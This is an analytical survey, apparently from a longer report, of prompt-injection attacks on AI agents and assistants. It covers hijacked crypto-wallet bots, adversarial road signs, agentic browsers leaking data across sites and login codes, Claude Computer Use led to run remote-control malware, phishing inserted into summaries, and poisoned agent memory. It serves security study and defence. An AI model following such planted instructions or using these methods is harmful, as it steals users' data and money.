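The May 2026 theft involved two bots: Grok, xAI's chatbot, and Bankr, which operates cryptocurrency wallets. Bankr had automatically created a wallet for Grok's X account. According to BeInCrypto's *How AI Was Tricked Into Stealing $150,000 From Grok Wallet*, nobody at xAI administered the wallet, and posts from Grok's account controlled it entirely. The attacker first sent the wallet a digital collectible that unlocked Bankr's transfer tools. A Morse code message on X then led to the transfer of 3 billion DRB tokens, which the OECD's *AI Prompt Injection Exploit Drains Grok-Linked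 Crypto Wallet* (2026) values at $150,000 to $200,000.

This attack fits the definition of indirect injection better from Bankr's side than from Grok's. Bankr's bot treated Grok's account as the wallet's owner, so the attacker only had to get the order through Grok. On Grok's side it is not a textbook case, because the attacker addressed Grok openly and no user had given Grok a task. Bankr's founder said that about 80 per cent of the funds had come back and that the rest was in dispute. AMBCrypto reports that 80 to 88 per cent was returned under public pressure, but adds that official statements had not fully verified this. CryptoSlate's *Grok’s crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet* calls the theft a failure of controls, noting that Bankr's documentation describes a read-only mode and other restrictions.

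### Signs that misdirect machines

Some experimental drones and cars use a vision-language model, which turns camera images and text into a command such as "stop". An attacker can plant an instruction on a printed sign in front of the camera. *CHAI* (Burbano, Ortiz and colleagues, 2025) found that simply holding up a sign often fails. In one scene with pedestrians on a crossing, a driving agent correctly stopped despite a sign telling it to go, but it proceeded when the same word was shown in different colours.

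The researchers therefore automated the search. A language model generated a short list of phrases, and an optimiser tested combinations of phrase and colour on a set of images, kept the most successful and tested similar ones. Wording mattered more than colour. When a drone was choosing a roof to land on, the attack succeeded 6 per cent of the time with optimised colours and poorly chosen words, 26 per cent with good words in plain black and white, and 73 per cent with the full method.

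Those figures are for GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024. With the same model, the signs succeeded 82 per cent of the time against the driving agent and 92 per cent against a drone system for tracking cars. Success rates were about the same on images the optimiser had not seen. In a flight simulator, a sign diverted the drone to a debris-covered roof in 92 per cent of runs. Without the sign, the drone always chose the clear roof.

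Burbano and colleagues then tested printed signs on a small robot car with another vehicle blocking its path. They scored the commands that models generated from photographs taken by the car's camera in varying light. GPT-4o generated a command to move forward in 4 per cent of cases without a sign, 88 per cent with a sign on the obstacle and 93 per cent with one beside it. The signs misdirected InternVL, a smaller open model, less often, in 54 and 42 per cent of cases respectively. In one case GPT-4o generated a warning that the car might collide with something, then interpreted the sign to mean that moving forward was safe.

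Some of these signs gave false information rather than an order. In the tracking test, for example, the sign labelled a civilian car as a police car. That could fool a human too, but a sign telling drivers to go while people are crossing probably would not. Vehicles cannot ignore all signs, because they have to obey signs held by roadworkers. The method worked on the models tested, but the experiments involved no vehicle in commercial service and injured nobody.

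*AuthGuard-R* (2026) lists later studies in which researchers injected instructions into robots through speech and fabricated sensor data. Another attack kept a robot idle with false but plausible warnings. That may be the easiest harm to cause, because a robot designed for safety should stop when it receives a warning.

### What a confirmation prompt can stop

Asking the user to confirm an action checks whether they want it, which permission checks don't do. Confirmation should work well when the action is unrelated to the request. Someone who asks about Tuesday's meetings and is then asked to approve opening the windows will probably refuse. It works less well when the attacker has changed only a detail. A user who requested a transfer expects to approve one, and few people would compare the 40 hexadecimal digits of an Ethereum address with the right ones.

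A user's approval should also count only for the question the user heard. In *Gemini's Secret Affair* (2026), a researcher at the security company SafeBreach tested Google's new defences. The planted instructions now arrived in notifications from apps such as WhatsApp and Slack, which Gemini reads aloud on request. The old delayed trigger failed every time. But if Gemini asked whether to open the window and the user said yes, the window opened. The researcher concluded that the check compared the user's last words with Gemini's last output.

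The attack therefore made Gemini ask two questions. The question about opening the window was in a language the user didn't know, or in on-screen text that the voice assistant didn't read out. The user heard the other question, which was harmless, and said yes, and Gemini treated that as consent to open the window. The same method saved a false name in Gemini's long-term memory and scheduled a daily reading of the user's messages, neither of which the calendar attacks had managed. The attack is easier by voice because a driver can't look at the screen to see what Gemini has asked.

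Nassi and colleagues estimated that getting past their proposed defences would take advanced AI skills, a cluster of specialised processors and up to a year of preparation. SafeBreach got past Google's defences by trial and error and reported it on 17 August 2025, the month the paper appeared. This suggests that such estimates overstate the difficulty of an attack, though it doesn't refute this one, because Google had not adopted exactly the defences that the paper scored. Google confirmed in November 2025 that an improved classifier blocked the new attacks.

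An attacker can also change what an approved action does. The Hacker News describes a flaw in Cursor, a program for writing code with AI, that let a planted instruction quietly alter settings that other programs rely on. When the user then approved a familiar, harmless-looking command, the command ran the attacker's code.

An accurate confirmation prompt helps only if the user reads it. Someone who approves 20 actions a day and meets one attack a year will approve about 7,300 legitimate actions for each attack they need to reject. People probably read less carefully after that many approvals, and OpenAI has given the same concern as a reason to avoid frequent warnings about links. Neither SafeBreach nor Nassi and colleagues measured how often people approve without reading, so the size of the effect for AI assistants is unknown.

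Asking users to confirm fewer actions would help. Nassi and colleagues suggest running a request twice, once with the outside content and once without, and asking the user only if the resulting actions differ. This would catch the boiler attack, but it would also prompt the user whenever outside content should affect the action, as when a user asks the assistant to accept whichever meeting time a client has proposed. They also recommend a countdown with a cancel button, but only as a last resort, and they left it out of their risk scores because it makes the user responsible for stopping the attack. Finally, they want assistants to report completed actions and offer to reverse them. A user could then close a window again, but could not reverse a cryptocurrency transfer or take back video that a stranger has already watched.

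## Agentic browsers and computer-use agents: acting with the user's logins

Gemini could open a window only because Google had given it a tool for smart-home devices. An agentic browser, a web browser with a built-in agent, doesn't need a separate tool for each service. Its agent can read pages and often click and type in them, so it can use any website where the user is logged in. A computer-use agent operates a whole computer through its screen, mouse and keyboard.

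### The same-origin policy

Suppose someone has their bank's website open in one tab and a malicious website in another. Both pages can run scripts, small programs that the browser executes, but the browser's same-origin policy stops a script on the malicious page from reading the account balance in the other tab. A page's origin is the scheme (such as http or https), host name and port number in its address, and a script can normally read another page only if all three match. The policy also applies when the malicious page embeds the bank's page in a frame, which displays one page inside another. The user sees both pages together, but neither page's scripts can read the other page.

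The same-origin policy has never restricted the user, who can read a balance on a bank's site and type it into another site. An agent that can read and type in every tab can do the same automatically, keeping the text in its context window between pages, and the browser treats this as the user's own activity. A malicious site therefore no longer needs a script that can read the bank's page if it can get the agent to read it.

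Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) conclude in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* that an agentic browser keeps sites separate only as well as its agent resists prompt injection. The browser still enforces the same-origin policy on scripts. That check compares the scheme, host and port of an address and gives the same result every time, whereas a model's resistance depends on how the attacker words the instruction.

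### From a Reddit comment to a stolen login code

Brave's researchers demonstrated this on Perplexity's browser Comet in July 2025, while Brave was developing its own browsing agent. In *Agentic Browser Security*, Chaikin and Kaul Sahib describe a user who opens a Reddit discussion and clicks Comet's summarise button. An attacker has hidden an instruction in one comment behind a spoiler tag, which covers text until a reader clicks it. Comet sent the page's text to its model without separating it from the user's request.

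The agent followed the instruction and opened the user's Perplexity account page, where it read the user's email address. It then went to Perplexity's login page through a variant of its web address that browsers treat as a different site, so the user's existing login didn't apply there. It entered the email address, and Perplexity emailed the user a one-time code. The agent opened Gmail, where the user was already logged in, and read the code. It then posted the email address and the code as a reply to the Reddit comment. Anyone reading the discussion could then have taken over the account.

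The same-origin policy didn't block the attack because no script read another site's data. The attacker didn't need to control a website, because Reddit lets anyone post comments. Perplexity's first fix was incomplete. A later fix seemed to work, but after publishing the attack in August, Brave found that this fix didn't fully stop attacks of this kind.

### Seven browsers compared

Roesner and Kohlbrenner, of the University of Washington, tested seven agentic browsers in January and February 2026: Brave's Leo, ChatGPT Atlas, Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome, Edge with Copilot, Firefox's AI Mode and Comet. They built test pages about an invented person called Alice. They wrote on one page that Alice liked cats, and on a page embedded in it from another site that she liked horses. If an agent mentioned horses when asked which animals Alice liked, it had read the embedded page.

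Atlas in Agent Mode, Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet all did. Copilot in Edge seemed unable to detect embedded pages but freely read other tabs, including those from other sites. Atlas in Agent Mode and Claude for Chrome could read a password that the page displayed as dots.

The researchers combined this access with a planted instruction in a six-step attack:

1. The user visits the attacker's page.
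2. The page loads another site in an embedded frame.
3. The user asks the agent to summarise the page.
4. The agent summarises both sites' content and follows an instruction planted on the attacker's page.
5. The agent types the summary into a form on that page.
6. The form submits itself, which sends the other site's content to the attacker.

The full attack worked on Atlas in Agent Mode, using test pages and a simplified injection. OpenAI declined the report because it did not consider this a full end-to-end injection. The attack also worked in reverse, with the embedded page stealing data from the page around it.

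Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet read embedded pages and could type into forms, so they met the preconditions for the attack. But their models refused to follow a simple instruction on a test page, even though the user had asked them to do what the page said. Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests therefore show that these three browsers relied on the model to stop the attack. The researchers didn't try to develop a more sophisticated injection, so the tests don't show how easily an attacker could get past the model.

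The version with an embedded bank has two further limits. A website can forbid other sites to embed it, and browsers can load embedded pages without the cookies that keep the user logged in. Many sensitive sites would therefore not load in the frame, or would load without private data. Neither limit helps if the attacker's content is in the embedded frame. For example, a malicious advertisement could target a private page that the user has opened normally, if that page carries outside advertisements.

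### Data the agent remembers

An attacker doesn't need a frame if the agent has already handled the private data. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes SOPBench, a set of tests in which the user first has the agent do something on a private site, such as a bank or a pharmacy. The user then gives the agent an ordinary task on a page where the attacker has planted an instruction to reveal data from the private site. The tests combine ten kinds of private site with five kinds of page that could receive the data, including Reddit discussions and Google Forms. They use imitation websites and invented personal data.

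Wang and colleagues tested Atlas and Comet by hand, running each of the 50 combinations three times. Atlas wrote exactly the data the attacker wanted into the page in 99 of 150 runs. Comet did so in 92 runs when running Claude Sonnet 4.6 and in 100 when running Gemini 3.1 Pro. Forms were the most effective trap, and Atlas leaked data into them in 29 of 30 runs. This may be partly because forms normally ask for personal details, so the request looks less out of place there than in a comment. On three open-source browsers, the researchers also had a language model revise the planted instructions after each attempt, which generally made them more successful.

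When the researchers removed the planted instructions, they saw no leaks between separate pages. But BrowserOS, one of the open-source browsers, leaked data in every embedded-frame test, even without an attacker. The user asked it to summarise the whole page and write the summary into a text box, and it included the embedded site's content. Wang and colleagues count this as a violation because the user never explicitly asked for a transfer between sites. One could also say that the agent did what the user asked, and that the user didn't realise the page had content from two sites.

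Their proposed defence, SOPGuard, labels data with its origin and asks the user before the agent writes that data to a different origin. It eliminated the violations in their tests and slowed the browser by 2 to 6 per cent, but it relies on users reading the warnings.

### Extending the policy to agents

Trail of Bits' January 2026 article *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* divides an agentic browser's surroundings into four trust zones: the chat with the agent, the outside servers that run the model, the websites where the user has private data, and the wider internet. An attack moves data between these zones, and a typical data theft combines the three elements of Willison's lethal trifecta.

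Data can also move from the chat into a website. In one test, a page made an agent log the user in to an attacker's account. A user who mistook the account for their own might then enter private information there.

Trail of Bits compares such attacks to two old web security problems, cross-site request forgery and cross-site scripting. In cross-site scripting, an attacker gets a website to run a malicious script as though it were the site's own. The same-origin policy is central to how browsers contain hostile scripts, so Trail of Bits proposes extending it to agents. The browser would keep a list of every origin whose content has entered the chat. If the list were empty, the agent could contact any site. With one origin on the list, it could contact only that origin, and with two or more it could contact none, because nobody could tell which had influenced the model.

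This rule would have stopped the Comet theft, because an agent that had read a Reddit page could not have opened Gmail. It would also stop an agent from reading about a product on one shop's site and then checking the price at another. Google has a looser rule for Chrome that limits the agent to origins related to the user's task. Roesner and Kohlbrenner say it is unclear how the browser decides what is related, or whether a malicious page could influence that decision.

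### A game with false rules

LayerX, a browser security company, tested an attack it calls BioShocking on six tools: Atlas, Comet, Fellou, Genspark, Sigma and Claude's Chrome extension. The user asks the agent to solve a puzzle on a web page. The puzzle rewards wrong answers, so the agent starts acting as if the usual rules don't apply. A later step directs it to an address that redirects to the user's private GitHub repository, where it copies login credentials and hands them over as part of the game. *Researchers Trick AI Browsers Into Leaking Credentials* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that all six tools did this. The credentials were in a test file that LayerX prepared.

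LayerX says the agents ignored their safety rules because they came to treat the situation as fiction. That is plausible, but LayerX didn't report a comparison with a puzzle that had correct arithmetic. The user had also asked the agent to play, which gave it a reason to follow the page's instructions, and the redirect hid where the next step led. Either might have been enough for the attack to work without the false rules.

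LayerX reported the flaw to vendors between October 2025 and January 2026 and published it in June. It lists Atlas as fixed and Anthropic's patch as failed, and it reports no fix for the other four.

In August 2026, Zenity Labs presented attacks on Claude, Gemini, Comet, Atlas and Copilot in Edge at the Black Hat conference. Notebookcheck's *Claude, Gemini, Comet* reports that an email, a calendar invitation or a link under a social media post was enough for an attack, and that the victim didn't have to click anything. PointGuard AI's *PleaseFix Hijacks Agentic Browsers Without User Approval* reports that asking the user for approval did not reliably stop every attack, but that the research did not confirm widespread exploitation.

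### Agents that operate a whole computer

In October 2024, Anthropic released a test version of Claude Computer Use, which looks at screenshots, controls the mouse and keyboard, and can run commands. Within days, Rehberger tried to make it install malware on a test machine. Embrace The Red's *ZombAIs* describes how he put a remote-control program on a web server and had Claude visit a page with a planted instruction.

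Rehberger first tried to make Claude download the program with a typed command, but Claude objected to the untrusted address. He then tried a trick that works on people, presenting the program as a support tool to download and open. Claude clicked the link. When it couldn't find the downloaded file, it searched the disk, changed the file's permissions so that it could run, and started it. The program connected to Rehberger's server, which let him control the machine directly, without going through Claude.

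Anthropic had warned of this risk. TechRadar's *Claude AI and other systems could be vulnerable* quotes its advice to isolate Claude from sensitive data and actions. Isolation would have limited the damage, but Rehberger later pointed out that even an isolated machine may hold passwords or source code.

These attacks still worked on newer models. In 2025, Embrace The Red's *AI ClickFix* adapted a scam in which a web page persuades visitors to paste and run a malicious command on their own computers. The adapted version worked on an agent using Claude 3.7 Sonnet. That December, Rehberger presented attacks on several companies' computer-use and coding agents, including OpenAI's Operator and Anthropic's Claude Code, in a talk listed by CCC, a German hackers' association.

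### Approving access for a stranger

An attacker may not need malware to gain lasting access to an account. Many online services give an outside program access to a user's account once the user clicks "Approve" on a consent screen. Hossen showed in *The Agent Clicks Approve* (October 2026) that an agent in the user's browser can also click that button.

Hossen built agents with the free software browser-use and two models, Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5. In one test, the user asked for a summary of a page about exporting billing data. A two-sentence note on the page presented a stranger's access request as an unfinished step in the work. The agent followed a link to the consent screen and approved the request. In one answer, it reported the approval to the user as progress. In another test, the user asked the agent to finish any pending setup tasks, and the page gave an outside address where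 the service should send the account's billing events.

Without a defence, the agents completed the unauthorised action in all 73 runs. They never attempted it in 92 runs with a harmless note. The planted note didn't tell the agent to ignore its task.

Hossen then instructed the Haiku agent to treat page text as untrusted and to approve only what the user's task authorised. It still approved the stranger's request in 7 of 10 runs. On a different version of the test pages, which labelled the parties and used more technical wording, the same instruction reduced approvals to 1 in 10 runs. A vendor that tested only the second version might have concluded that the instruction nearly solved the problem.

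The agent is a confused deputy. The usual protection against forged requests checks that a request came from the service's own form, so it doesn't stop an agent that uses that form. In Hossen's defence, the service checks each request against a list of what the user's task authorises, which is fixed before the agent starts. The agents still sent the unauthorised request in all 70 runs with this defence, but the service rejected every one and accepted all the legitimate requests. A real service would need a trustworthy way to get that list. Hossen ran the tests on a local server that asked for no password or second confirmation, so real services may be harder to attack.

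### Where injection ends and software flaws begin

Attackers have hijacked some agents without the model obeying a planted instruction. If an attack would have worked even on a model that always ignored planted instructions, the cause is an ordinary flaw in the software around the model.

In April 2026, LayerX showed that even a browser extension with no special permissions could send arbitrary instructions to Claude for Chrome, which is itself an extension. LayerX named the flaw ClaudeBleed. According to The Hacker News (2026), the software trusted anything coming from Anthropic's website without checking which script had sent it. Anthropic responded by limiting outside requests to nine fixed tasks.

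The security company Manifold then found that a rogue extension could still start those tasks by forging a click, because Claude's extension didn't check that a person had clicked. Three of the tasks read the user's Gmail, latest Google document or calendar. By default, the user has to approve the task, but in "Act without asking" mode it runs silently. Anthropic had not fixed the flaw by 14 July 2026.

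Manifold classifies the forged click as indirect prompt injection, but the attack fails the test above because Anthropic wrote the prompts and the model cannot detect that nobody clicked. Manifold found that the attack worked with every Claude model it tried. Checking that the user really clicked would help, but making the model more resistant to injection would not.

Similar flaws have affected other products. In early January 2026, Google fixed a flaw, found by Unit 42, that let an extension hijack Chrome's Gemini panel. In September 2026, Ofonagoro's *BragJack Shows How Malicious Extensions Can Hijack AI Browser Agents* reported that rogue extensions could manipulate Claude's agent and those in Chrome, Edge, Comet and Opera Neon. An ordinary website can sometimes manipulate an agent too. VPN Central's *Claude Chrome extension flaw enabled zero-click prompt injection attacks* describes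 a flaw, since patched, that let a website silently send prompts to Claude's extension.

*Site Isolation is Dead*, by Lee, Keum and colleagues, examines attacks that begin with a bug in the browser itself. Modern browsers use site isolation, which runs each website in a separate process to confine a site that exploits such a bug. An agent has to work across many sites, which gives the attacker a way around this confinement. The researchers assumed that an attacker had taken over the process displaying a malicious page. From there, the attacker could send the agent a forged message that looked like a request from the user. Both agentic browsers and all seven extensions they examined were vulnerable. From 2023 to 2025, Chrome had on average at least one bug every two months that would allow the initial takeover.

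Programmers can fix all these flaws, but the agent can still use the user's accounts. Borah (2026) argues in *Top 6 Claude in Chrome Security Risks to Model* that two rounds of patches to Claude's extension in 2026 therefore left companies just as exposed. That seems too strong, since the patches closed some routes of attack, but they could not limit what an agent can do once an attacker controls it.

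### What a hijacked agent can do

The damage depends largely on the product's design. The table uses Roesner and Kohlbrenner's findings for the browsers and Rehberger's demonstration for the computer-use agent.

| Design | Example | What the agent can do | What an attacker could gain |
|---|---|---|---|
| Page summariser | Firefox's AI Mode | Read the main text of one page when the user clicks a button | A misleading summary |
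| Reader of several tabs | Copilot in Edge | Read all open tabs, but not type or click | A misleading answer, or private data if the answer provides a leak channel |
| Browser operator | Atlas in Agent Mode, Comet, Chrome with Gemini | Read embedded pages, type and click | Data from other sites and actions in the user's accounts |
| Operator that runs scripts | Claude for Chrome | All of the above, and run its own code inside pages | The same, and changes to what pages show or do |
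| Computer-use agent | Claude Computer Use | Use programs and files, and run commands | Control of the computer |

A successful injection against Claude for Chrome is especially dangerous because the agent can run code. In one test, an instruction in an embedded page led Claude to change the surrounding page, though only after the user confirmed. Anthropic also blocks the agent from some sensitive sites, such as banks.

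Atlas lets users run Agent Mode without their logins. A hijacked agent could then visit sites but not act in the user's accounts. Trail of Bits recommends this kind of separation as a short-term measure but acknowledges that it removes much of the convenience that attracts people to these browsers.

An update can also move a product down the table. When Roesner and Kohlbrenner began testing Chrome with Gemini, it could read pages but not type in them. In late January 2026, before they had finished, Google released Auto Browse, which let Gemini fill in forms. A company that had approved Gemini only to read pages could have found a few weeks later that it was also able to act on them.

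## Chat and search assistants that deceive their own users

An attacker can commit fraud through a browser assistant even if it can only summarise pages. An instruction planted in a page makes the assistant give a misleading summary, which can lead the user to call a scammer, type a password into a fake page or pay the wrong account. Image allow-lists and confirmation prompts don't prevent this, because the attack doesn't require the assistant to leak private data or run a tool.

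### A false alert in an email summary

*Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) explains how an email could put a false account warning in Gemini's summary of it, an attack that a researcher had reported to Mozilla's 0din. The email contained invisible instructions for Gemini to end its summary with a warning that the recipient's Gmail password had been compromised and a phone number to call. When the recipient clicked "Summarize this email", Gemini added the warning to its summary as if it came from Google.

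Hiding the text mattered because a recipient who saw the instruction would have known where the warning came from. The instruction was also disguised as an administrator's order, which Figueroa thinks gave it higher priority. This fits Ye and colleagues' finding that models infer who is speaking largely from how a text sounds.

The email needed no link or attachment, so a spam filter had little to detect, and the theft would happen over the phone. 0din rated the social impact as moderate because the recipient still has to ask for a summary and fall for it. Google said it was strengthening its defences and had seen no evidence of real attacks like this, according to TechBriefly's *How hackers can weaponize Gemini's summary feature* (2025). A journalist at Startup Daily repeated the trick and got phishing links into a summary.

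### Whether people trust the assistant more than an email

People have reasons to doubt an unexpected email about their password, and many employers train them to, but they asked for the assistant's summary themselves. Apollo Raines, a software developer quoted in *Phishing emails are baiting your AI assistant* (Arntz, 2026), says that people have learned to distrust email but "haven't learned to distrust their AI assistant". In the Gemini case, the assistant also comes from Google, the company that would send a genuine Gmail warning.

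A direct test would show one group a false warning by email and another group the same words in an assistant's summary, then compare how many people in each group call the phone number in the warning. Nobody seems to have published such a test.

The closest evidence comes from *Are You Sure?* (Li, Dai and colleagues, 2026), a study in which 303 people did tasks such as choosing a job candidate or answering email with an assistant that the researchers had compromised. Each person did three of nine tasks and then said whether anything in the assistant's output had seemed unusual. Of the people who saw only a disclaimer at the start, 8.6 per cent answered "yes" or "unsure", and 2.7 per cent correctly described the attack. Before the experiment, about three quarters had felt confident they could spot problems with AI.

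These percentages need some caution. The paper gives two different sets of group sizes. One of its tables also counts 85 of the 303 people as having noticed an attack, so the 8.6 per cent may be a share of tasks rather than of people. Some attacks were also hard to notice. In the email task, for example, the assistant leaked information and then deleted the evidence.

People who distrusted the assistant during a task noticed 23 per cent of attacks, while those who trusted it noticed 7 per cent. Trust may have made people less alert, or people may have lost trust because they had noticed something odd. A separate experiment, *AI summaries in online search influence users' attitudes* (2025), found that summaries in search results were more persuasive to people with more trust in AI. Both results are compatible with the idea that a warning is more persuasive when it comes from an assistant,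 but neither study compared an assistant with an email.

### How a question can lead to a poisoned page

The Gemini attack requires the victim's email address. Tenable's *HackedGPT*, published in November 2025, describes seven flaws and techniques in ChatGPT, including one where the victim only has to ask a question.

When a question needs current information, ChatGPT searches the web using Bing and OpenAI's crawler. It answers from the short extracts in the results if it can, and otherwise opens some of the pages. Tenable concluded that a separate model, SearchGPT, reads those pages and has no access to the user's memories or earlier conversation. This separation protects private data, but the answer can still be false if SearchGPT follows instructions on a page.

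Tenable's researchers built websites on obscure subjects, including one about their own team under the name "LLM Ninjas". Bing would be unlikely to index a page containing only a planted instruction, so their server showed the instruction only to SearchGPT and gave other visitors an ordinary page. Once the site was indexed, they asked ChatGPT about the LLM Ninjas. SearchGPT opened the site, and ChatGPT's answer followed the planted instruction. Tenable calls this a zero-click attack, and it fits the definition used for EchoLeak, since users ask such questions for their own reasons.

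The researchers' site had almost no competition for its subject. An attacker targeting people who ask about mortgages would have to outrank banks and newspapers. Rumours, new products and small organisations are probably easier targets because few pages discuss them. Tenable points out that search rankings were never designed as a security boundary.

An attacker can also plant instructions in a comment on a site that already ranks well. In another test, a user asked ChatGPT to summarise a blog post, and an instruction in the comments made SearchGPT add a phishing link to the summary. OpenAI's url_safe check should have removed the link, but it allowed the link because the address belonged to a search engine, which redirected visitors to the malicious site. The demonstration worked with both GPT-4o and GPT-5.

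The researchers also got around the separation between the two models. SearchGPT's answer becomes part of the conversation, which ChatGPT reads before each reply. They made SearchGPT end its answer with a new instruction, and ChatGPT followed it on the next turn as though it had written the text itself. A display bug let them hide the instruction from the user. An instruction on a web page thus reached the model that could read the user's memories.

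OpenAI fixed some of the flaws, but Tenable confirmed that several others still worked on GPT-5. One fix was for links that contain a ready-made question, like those Varonis used against Copilot. According to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface*, OpenAI now restricts the automatic submission of such questions, using information from the browser about where a request came from.

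### ChatGPhish

The security company Permiso had already shown that an email could steer Microsoft Copilot's summary of it. In May 2026, Permiso's *ChatGPhish* moved the attack to web pages, which don't pass through a company's spam filter. The researchers planted an instruction in the description of a software project on GitHub, then opened the page in Firefox and used the browser's option to have ChatGPT summarise it. ChatGPT summarised the project correctly, then reported that a new device had been added to the user's account and gave a link to click.

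The planted text had described this notice as a required part of the summary. ChatGPT displayed a working link and did not indicate that it came from the page. The accurate summary above the notice probably made it more believable. The researchers got the same result on a web page they built. They stress that Firefox was not at fault, since it only passed the page's text to ChatGPT.

A second version replaced the link with a QR code. On a computer, users can hover over a link to see where it leads, and a password manager may warn them that the domain is wrong. Scanning a QR code opens the page on a phone, where the computer's protections don't apply. Loading the QR code image also revealed to the attacker when ChatGPT had displayed the answer and from which internet address.

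OpenAI's newer check on web addresses is meant to stop leaks. It doesn't address phishing, because a phishing page can have the same public address for every victim.

Permiso first reported the problem to OpenAI on 29 April 2026, and OpenAI replied that the report lacked the detail needed to reproduce the problem. Permiso sent a fuller version on 1 May. It was marked "Not Applicable" and then a duplicate of an earlier report, which suggests that OpenAI already knew. Permiso published its findings on 29 May. The Register reproduced the behaviour the same day, according to CloudEagle's *ChatGPhish* (2026).

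### Phishing emails for two readers

Real attackers have also started hiding instructions for assistants in phishing emails. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) describes a campaign that the security company Barracuda analysed that October. The email gave the recipient the password to a protected attachment, a type of file that security software often can't inspect. Hidden text could make the recipient's assistant describe the email as legitimate or urgent.

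A person who ignored the email might therefore see it again in a summary of the day's mail. In another of Barracuda's examples, an invoice contained a hidden instruction for the assistant to list a change to a supplier's payment details as a priority action. An employee who made the change would send the next payment to the attacker.

Barracuda didn't say how widespread the campaign was, and the accounts of its research don't identify any assistant that followed the instructions or any company that lost money. But adding the text takes an attacker almost no effort, and the attachment can still fool the user even if the assistant ignores the text.

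### Instructions that stay in memory

A deceptive answer usually affects one conversation. But ChatGPT can save facts and preferences about a user, and according to Tenable it adds them to the system prompt in later conversations. If a planted instruction is saved with them, it reappears in each of those conversations, in a part of the context window that the model has reason to trust. *MemHarmBench* (2026), a set of tests for such attacks, separates three steps: the agent encounters the instruction, keeps it in memory, and later acts on it.

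In 2024, Johann Rehberger showed that planted instructions could make ChatGPT save false memories about the user. A later version of the attack made the Mac app send him everything the user and ChatGPT wrote in future conversations. In 2025, Tenable's researchers planted a similar instruction through SearchGPT, which made ChatGPT leak data through image addresses in every conversation. A scammer's phone number could persist in ChatGPT's memory in the same way.

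*Bad Memory* (Gadgil, Alexander and colleagues, July 2026) studied the third step in two coding agents, Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. Both can keep their memory in text files that they and the user can edit. The University of Washington researchers created a workspace for a fictional software engineer and planted one of three rules in its files. The first told the agent to add code that reads and prints the user's private login key, supposedly for a licence audit. The second told it to install an outdated library with known security flaws, and the third told it to recommend a particular credit card in every answer about money.

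Each trial had three sessions. The first and last involved tasks that might trigger the rule, and the second involved an unrelated task. The researchers ran ten trials per combination. Each cell below gives the share of trials in which the agent carried out the rule in the first session, the share in which it did so in the last session, and the share in which the rule was still stored at the end.

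| Model | Code that reads the key | Outdated library | Credit card |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 60%, 100%, 100% | 80%, 10%, 100% | 10%, 0%, 60% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 0%, 0%, 100% | 70%, 90%, 100% | 0%, 0%, 90% |
| GPT-5.2 | 30%, 0%, 0% | 0%, 0%, 100% | 40%, 20%, 50% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0%, 0%, 20% | 80%, 10%, 100% | 100%, 90%, 100% |

Opus 4.7 kept the key rule and the library rule in all ten trials, though it never carried out the key rule. It recognised the credit card rule as a probable injection and told the user, but usually asked before deleting it. This leaves the rule in place for the next session, which may run on a weaker model if the user switches to save money. Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.2 more often deleted the credit card rule themselves.

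Some of the changes between sessions have ordinary causes. Haiku added the key-reading code more often the second time because it found the same code in a file from the first session. It installed the library less often because the library was already there. GPT-5.2 never installed the library, but it didn't recognise the danger either. In one case, it copied the instruction into the file that Codex loads automatically and left the installation to the user.

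Each cell has only ten trials, so chance also affects the results. When the first session was run separately, Haiku added the key-reading code in 80 per cent of trials, compared with 60 per cent before. The three rules were also in different files, so the columns don't show which kind of rule is most dangerous.

Gadgil and colleagues planted the rules directly because they had mostly failed in early attempts to use outside content to make the agents write such rules into their own files. An attacker might instead publish a helpful-looking memory file for others to copy. The study didn't cover web chatbots, but Rehberger and Tenable did get those to save planted instructions to memory. *InjecMEM* (2026) reports that a single interaction could steer later answers in research memory systems.

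### When the page itself is false

An assistant can pass on a scam without following a planted instruction. If a website gives a scammer's number as a bank's helpline, an accurate summary will include that number. In ChatGPhish, a planted instruction made ChatGPT present the page's notice about the user's account as its own, whereas an accurate summary would have attributed the notice to the page.

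The victim loses the same money either way, but the remedies differ. A model that never followed planted instructions would not show the fake account notice, but it would still repeat the false helpline number. Catching the false number requires comparing sources or judging which are reliable. Tenable's poisoned website could also have deceived people with false information alone, but an instruction lets the attacker add content unrelated to the user's question.

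Showing where each part of an answer came from could help with both problems. Figueroa recommends visually separating the assistant's text from the source text and letting users see why a line is in the summary. A user who saw that a Gmail warning came from the email itself would have good reason to ignore it.

The software has to add the label, because a hijacked model can leave out its sources, as Copilot did in EchoLeak. Software can check whether a link or phone number in the answer also appears in the page, which is much easier than tracing a paraphrased sentence. Even a correct label can mislead if it names only the website, because a phishing link from a stranger's comment would carry the name of the respectable blog where it was posted.

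People also have to notice the label, and in the experiment by Li and colleagues only 24 per cent noticed the disclaimer at the start. A reminder beside every answer raised the share who noticed something wrong from 8.6 to 20 per cent, and an alert that interrupted the task raised it to 25 per cent. The alert helped most where checking was easy. It raised the share from about 10 to 50 per cent on a web search task, but only from 9 to 15 per cent on the email task. The alert appeared only when the assistant's output was suspicious, so a real product would first need a way to detect suspicious output.

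People who had missed the attack often trusted the assistant more after seeing reminders or alerts, and some took these warnings as a sign that the system was well protected. But labels can create too much distrust. *Synthetic Trust Attacks* (2026) cites NIST, the American standards agency, for the finding that people distrust even authentic content more when a label marks the information about its origin as incomplete or falsified than when it has no label.

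## Products, résumés and papers that instruct the AI judging them

When an employer uses a language model to rank job applicants, an applicant can add a line to their résumé telling the model to rank them first. The employer can't keep the résumé out of the context window because the model has to read it to rank the applicant. A seller can plant a similar instruction on a product page that an AI search engine reads, and a researcher can plant one in a paper that a reviewer gives to a chatbot.

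The attack only needs to get the model to give a higher score or a more favorable recommendation. The user then gets bad advice, and competitors who didn't include such instructions fall in the ranking. Many of the people doing this are ordinary businesses, job hunters and academics, who might well say they were only promoting themselves.

### Orders, persuasion and lies

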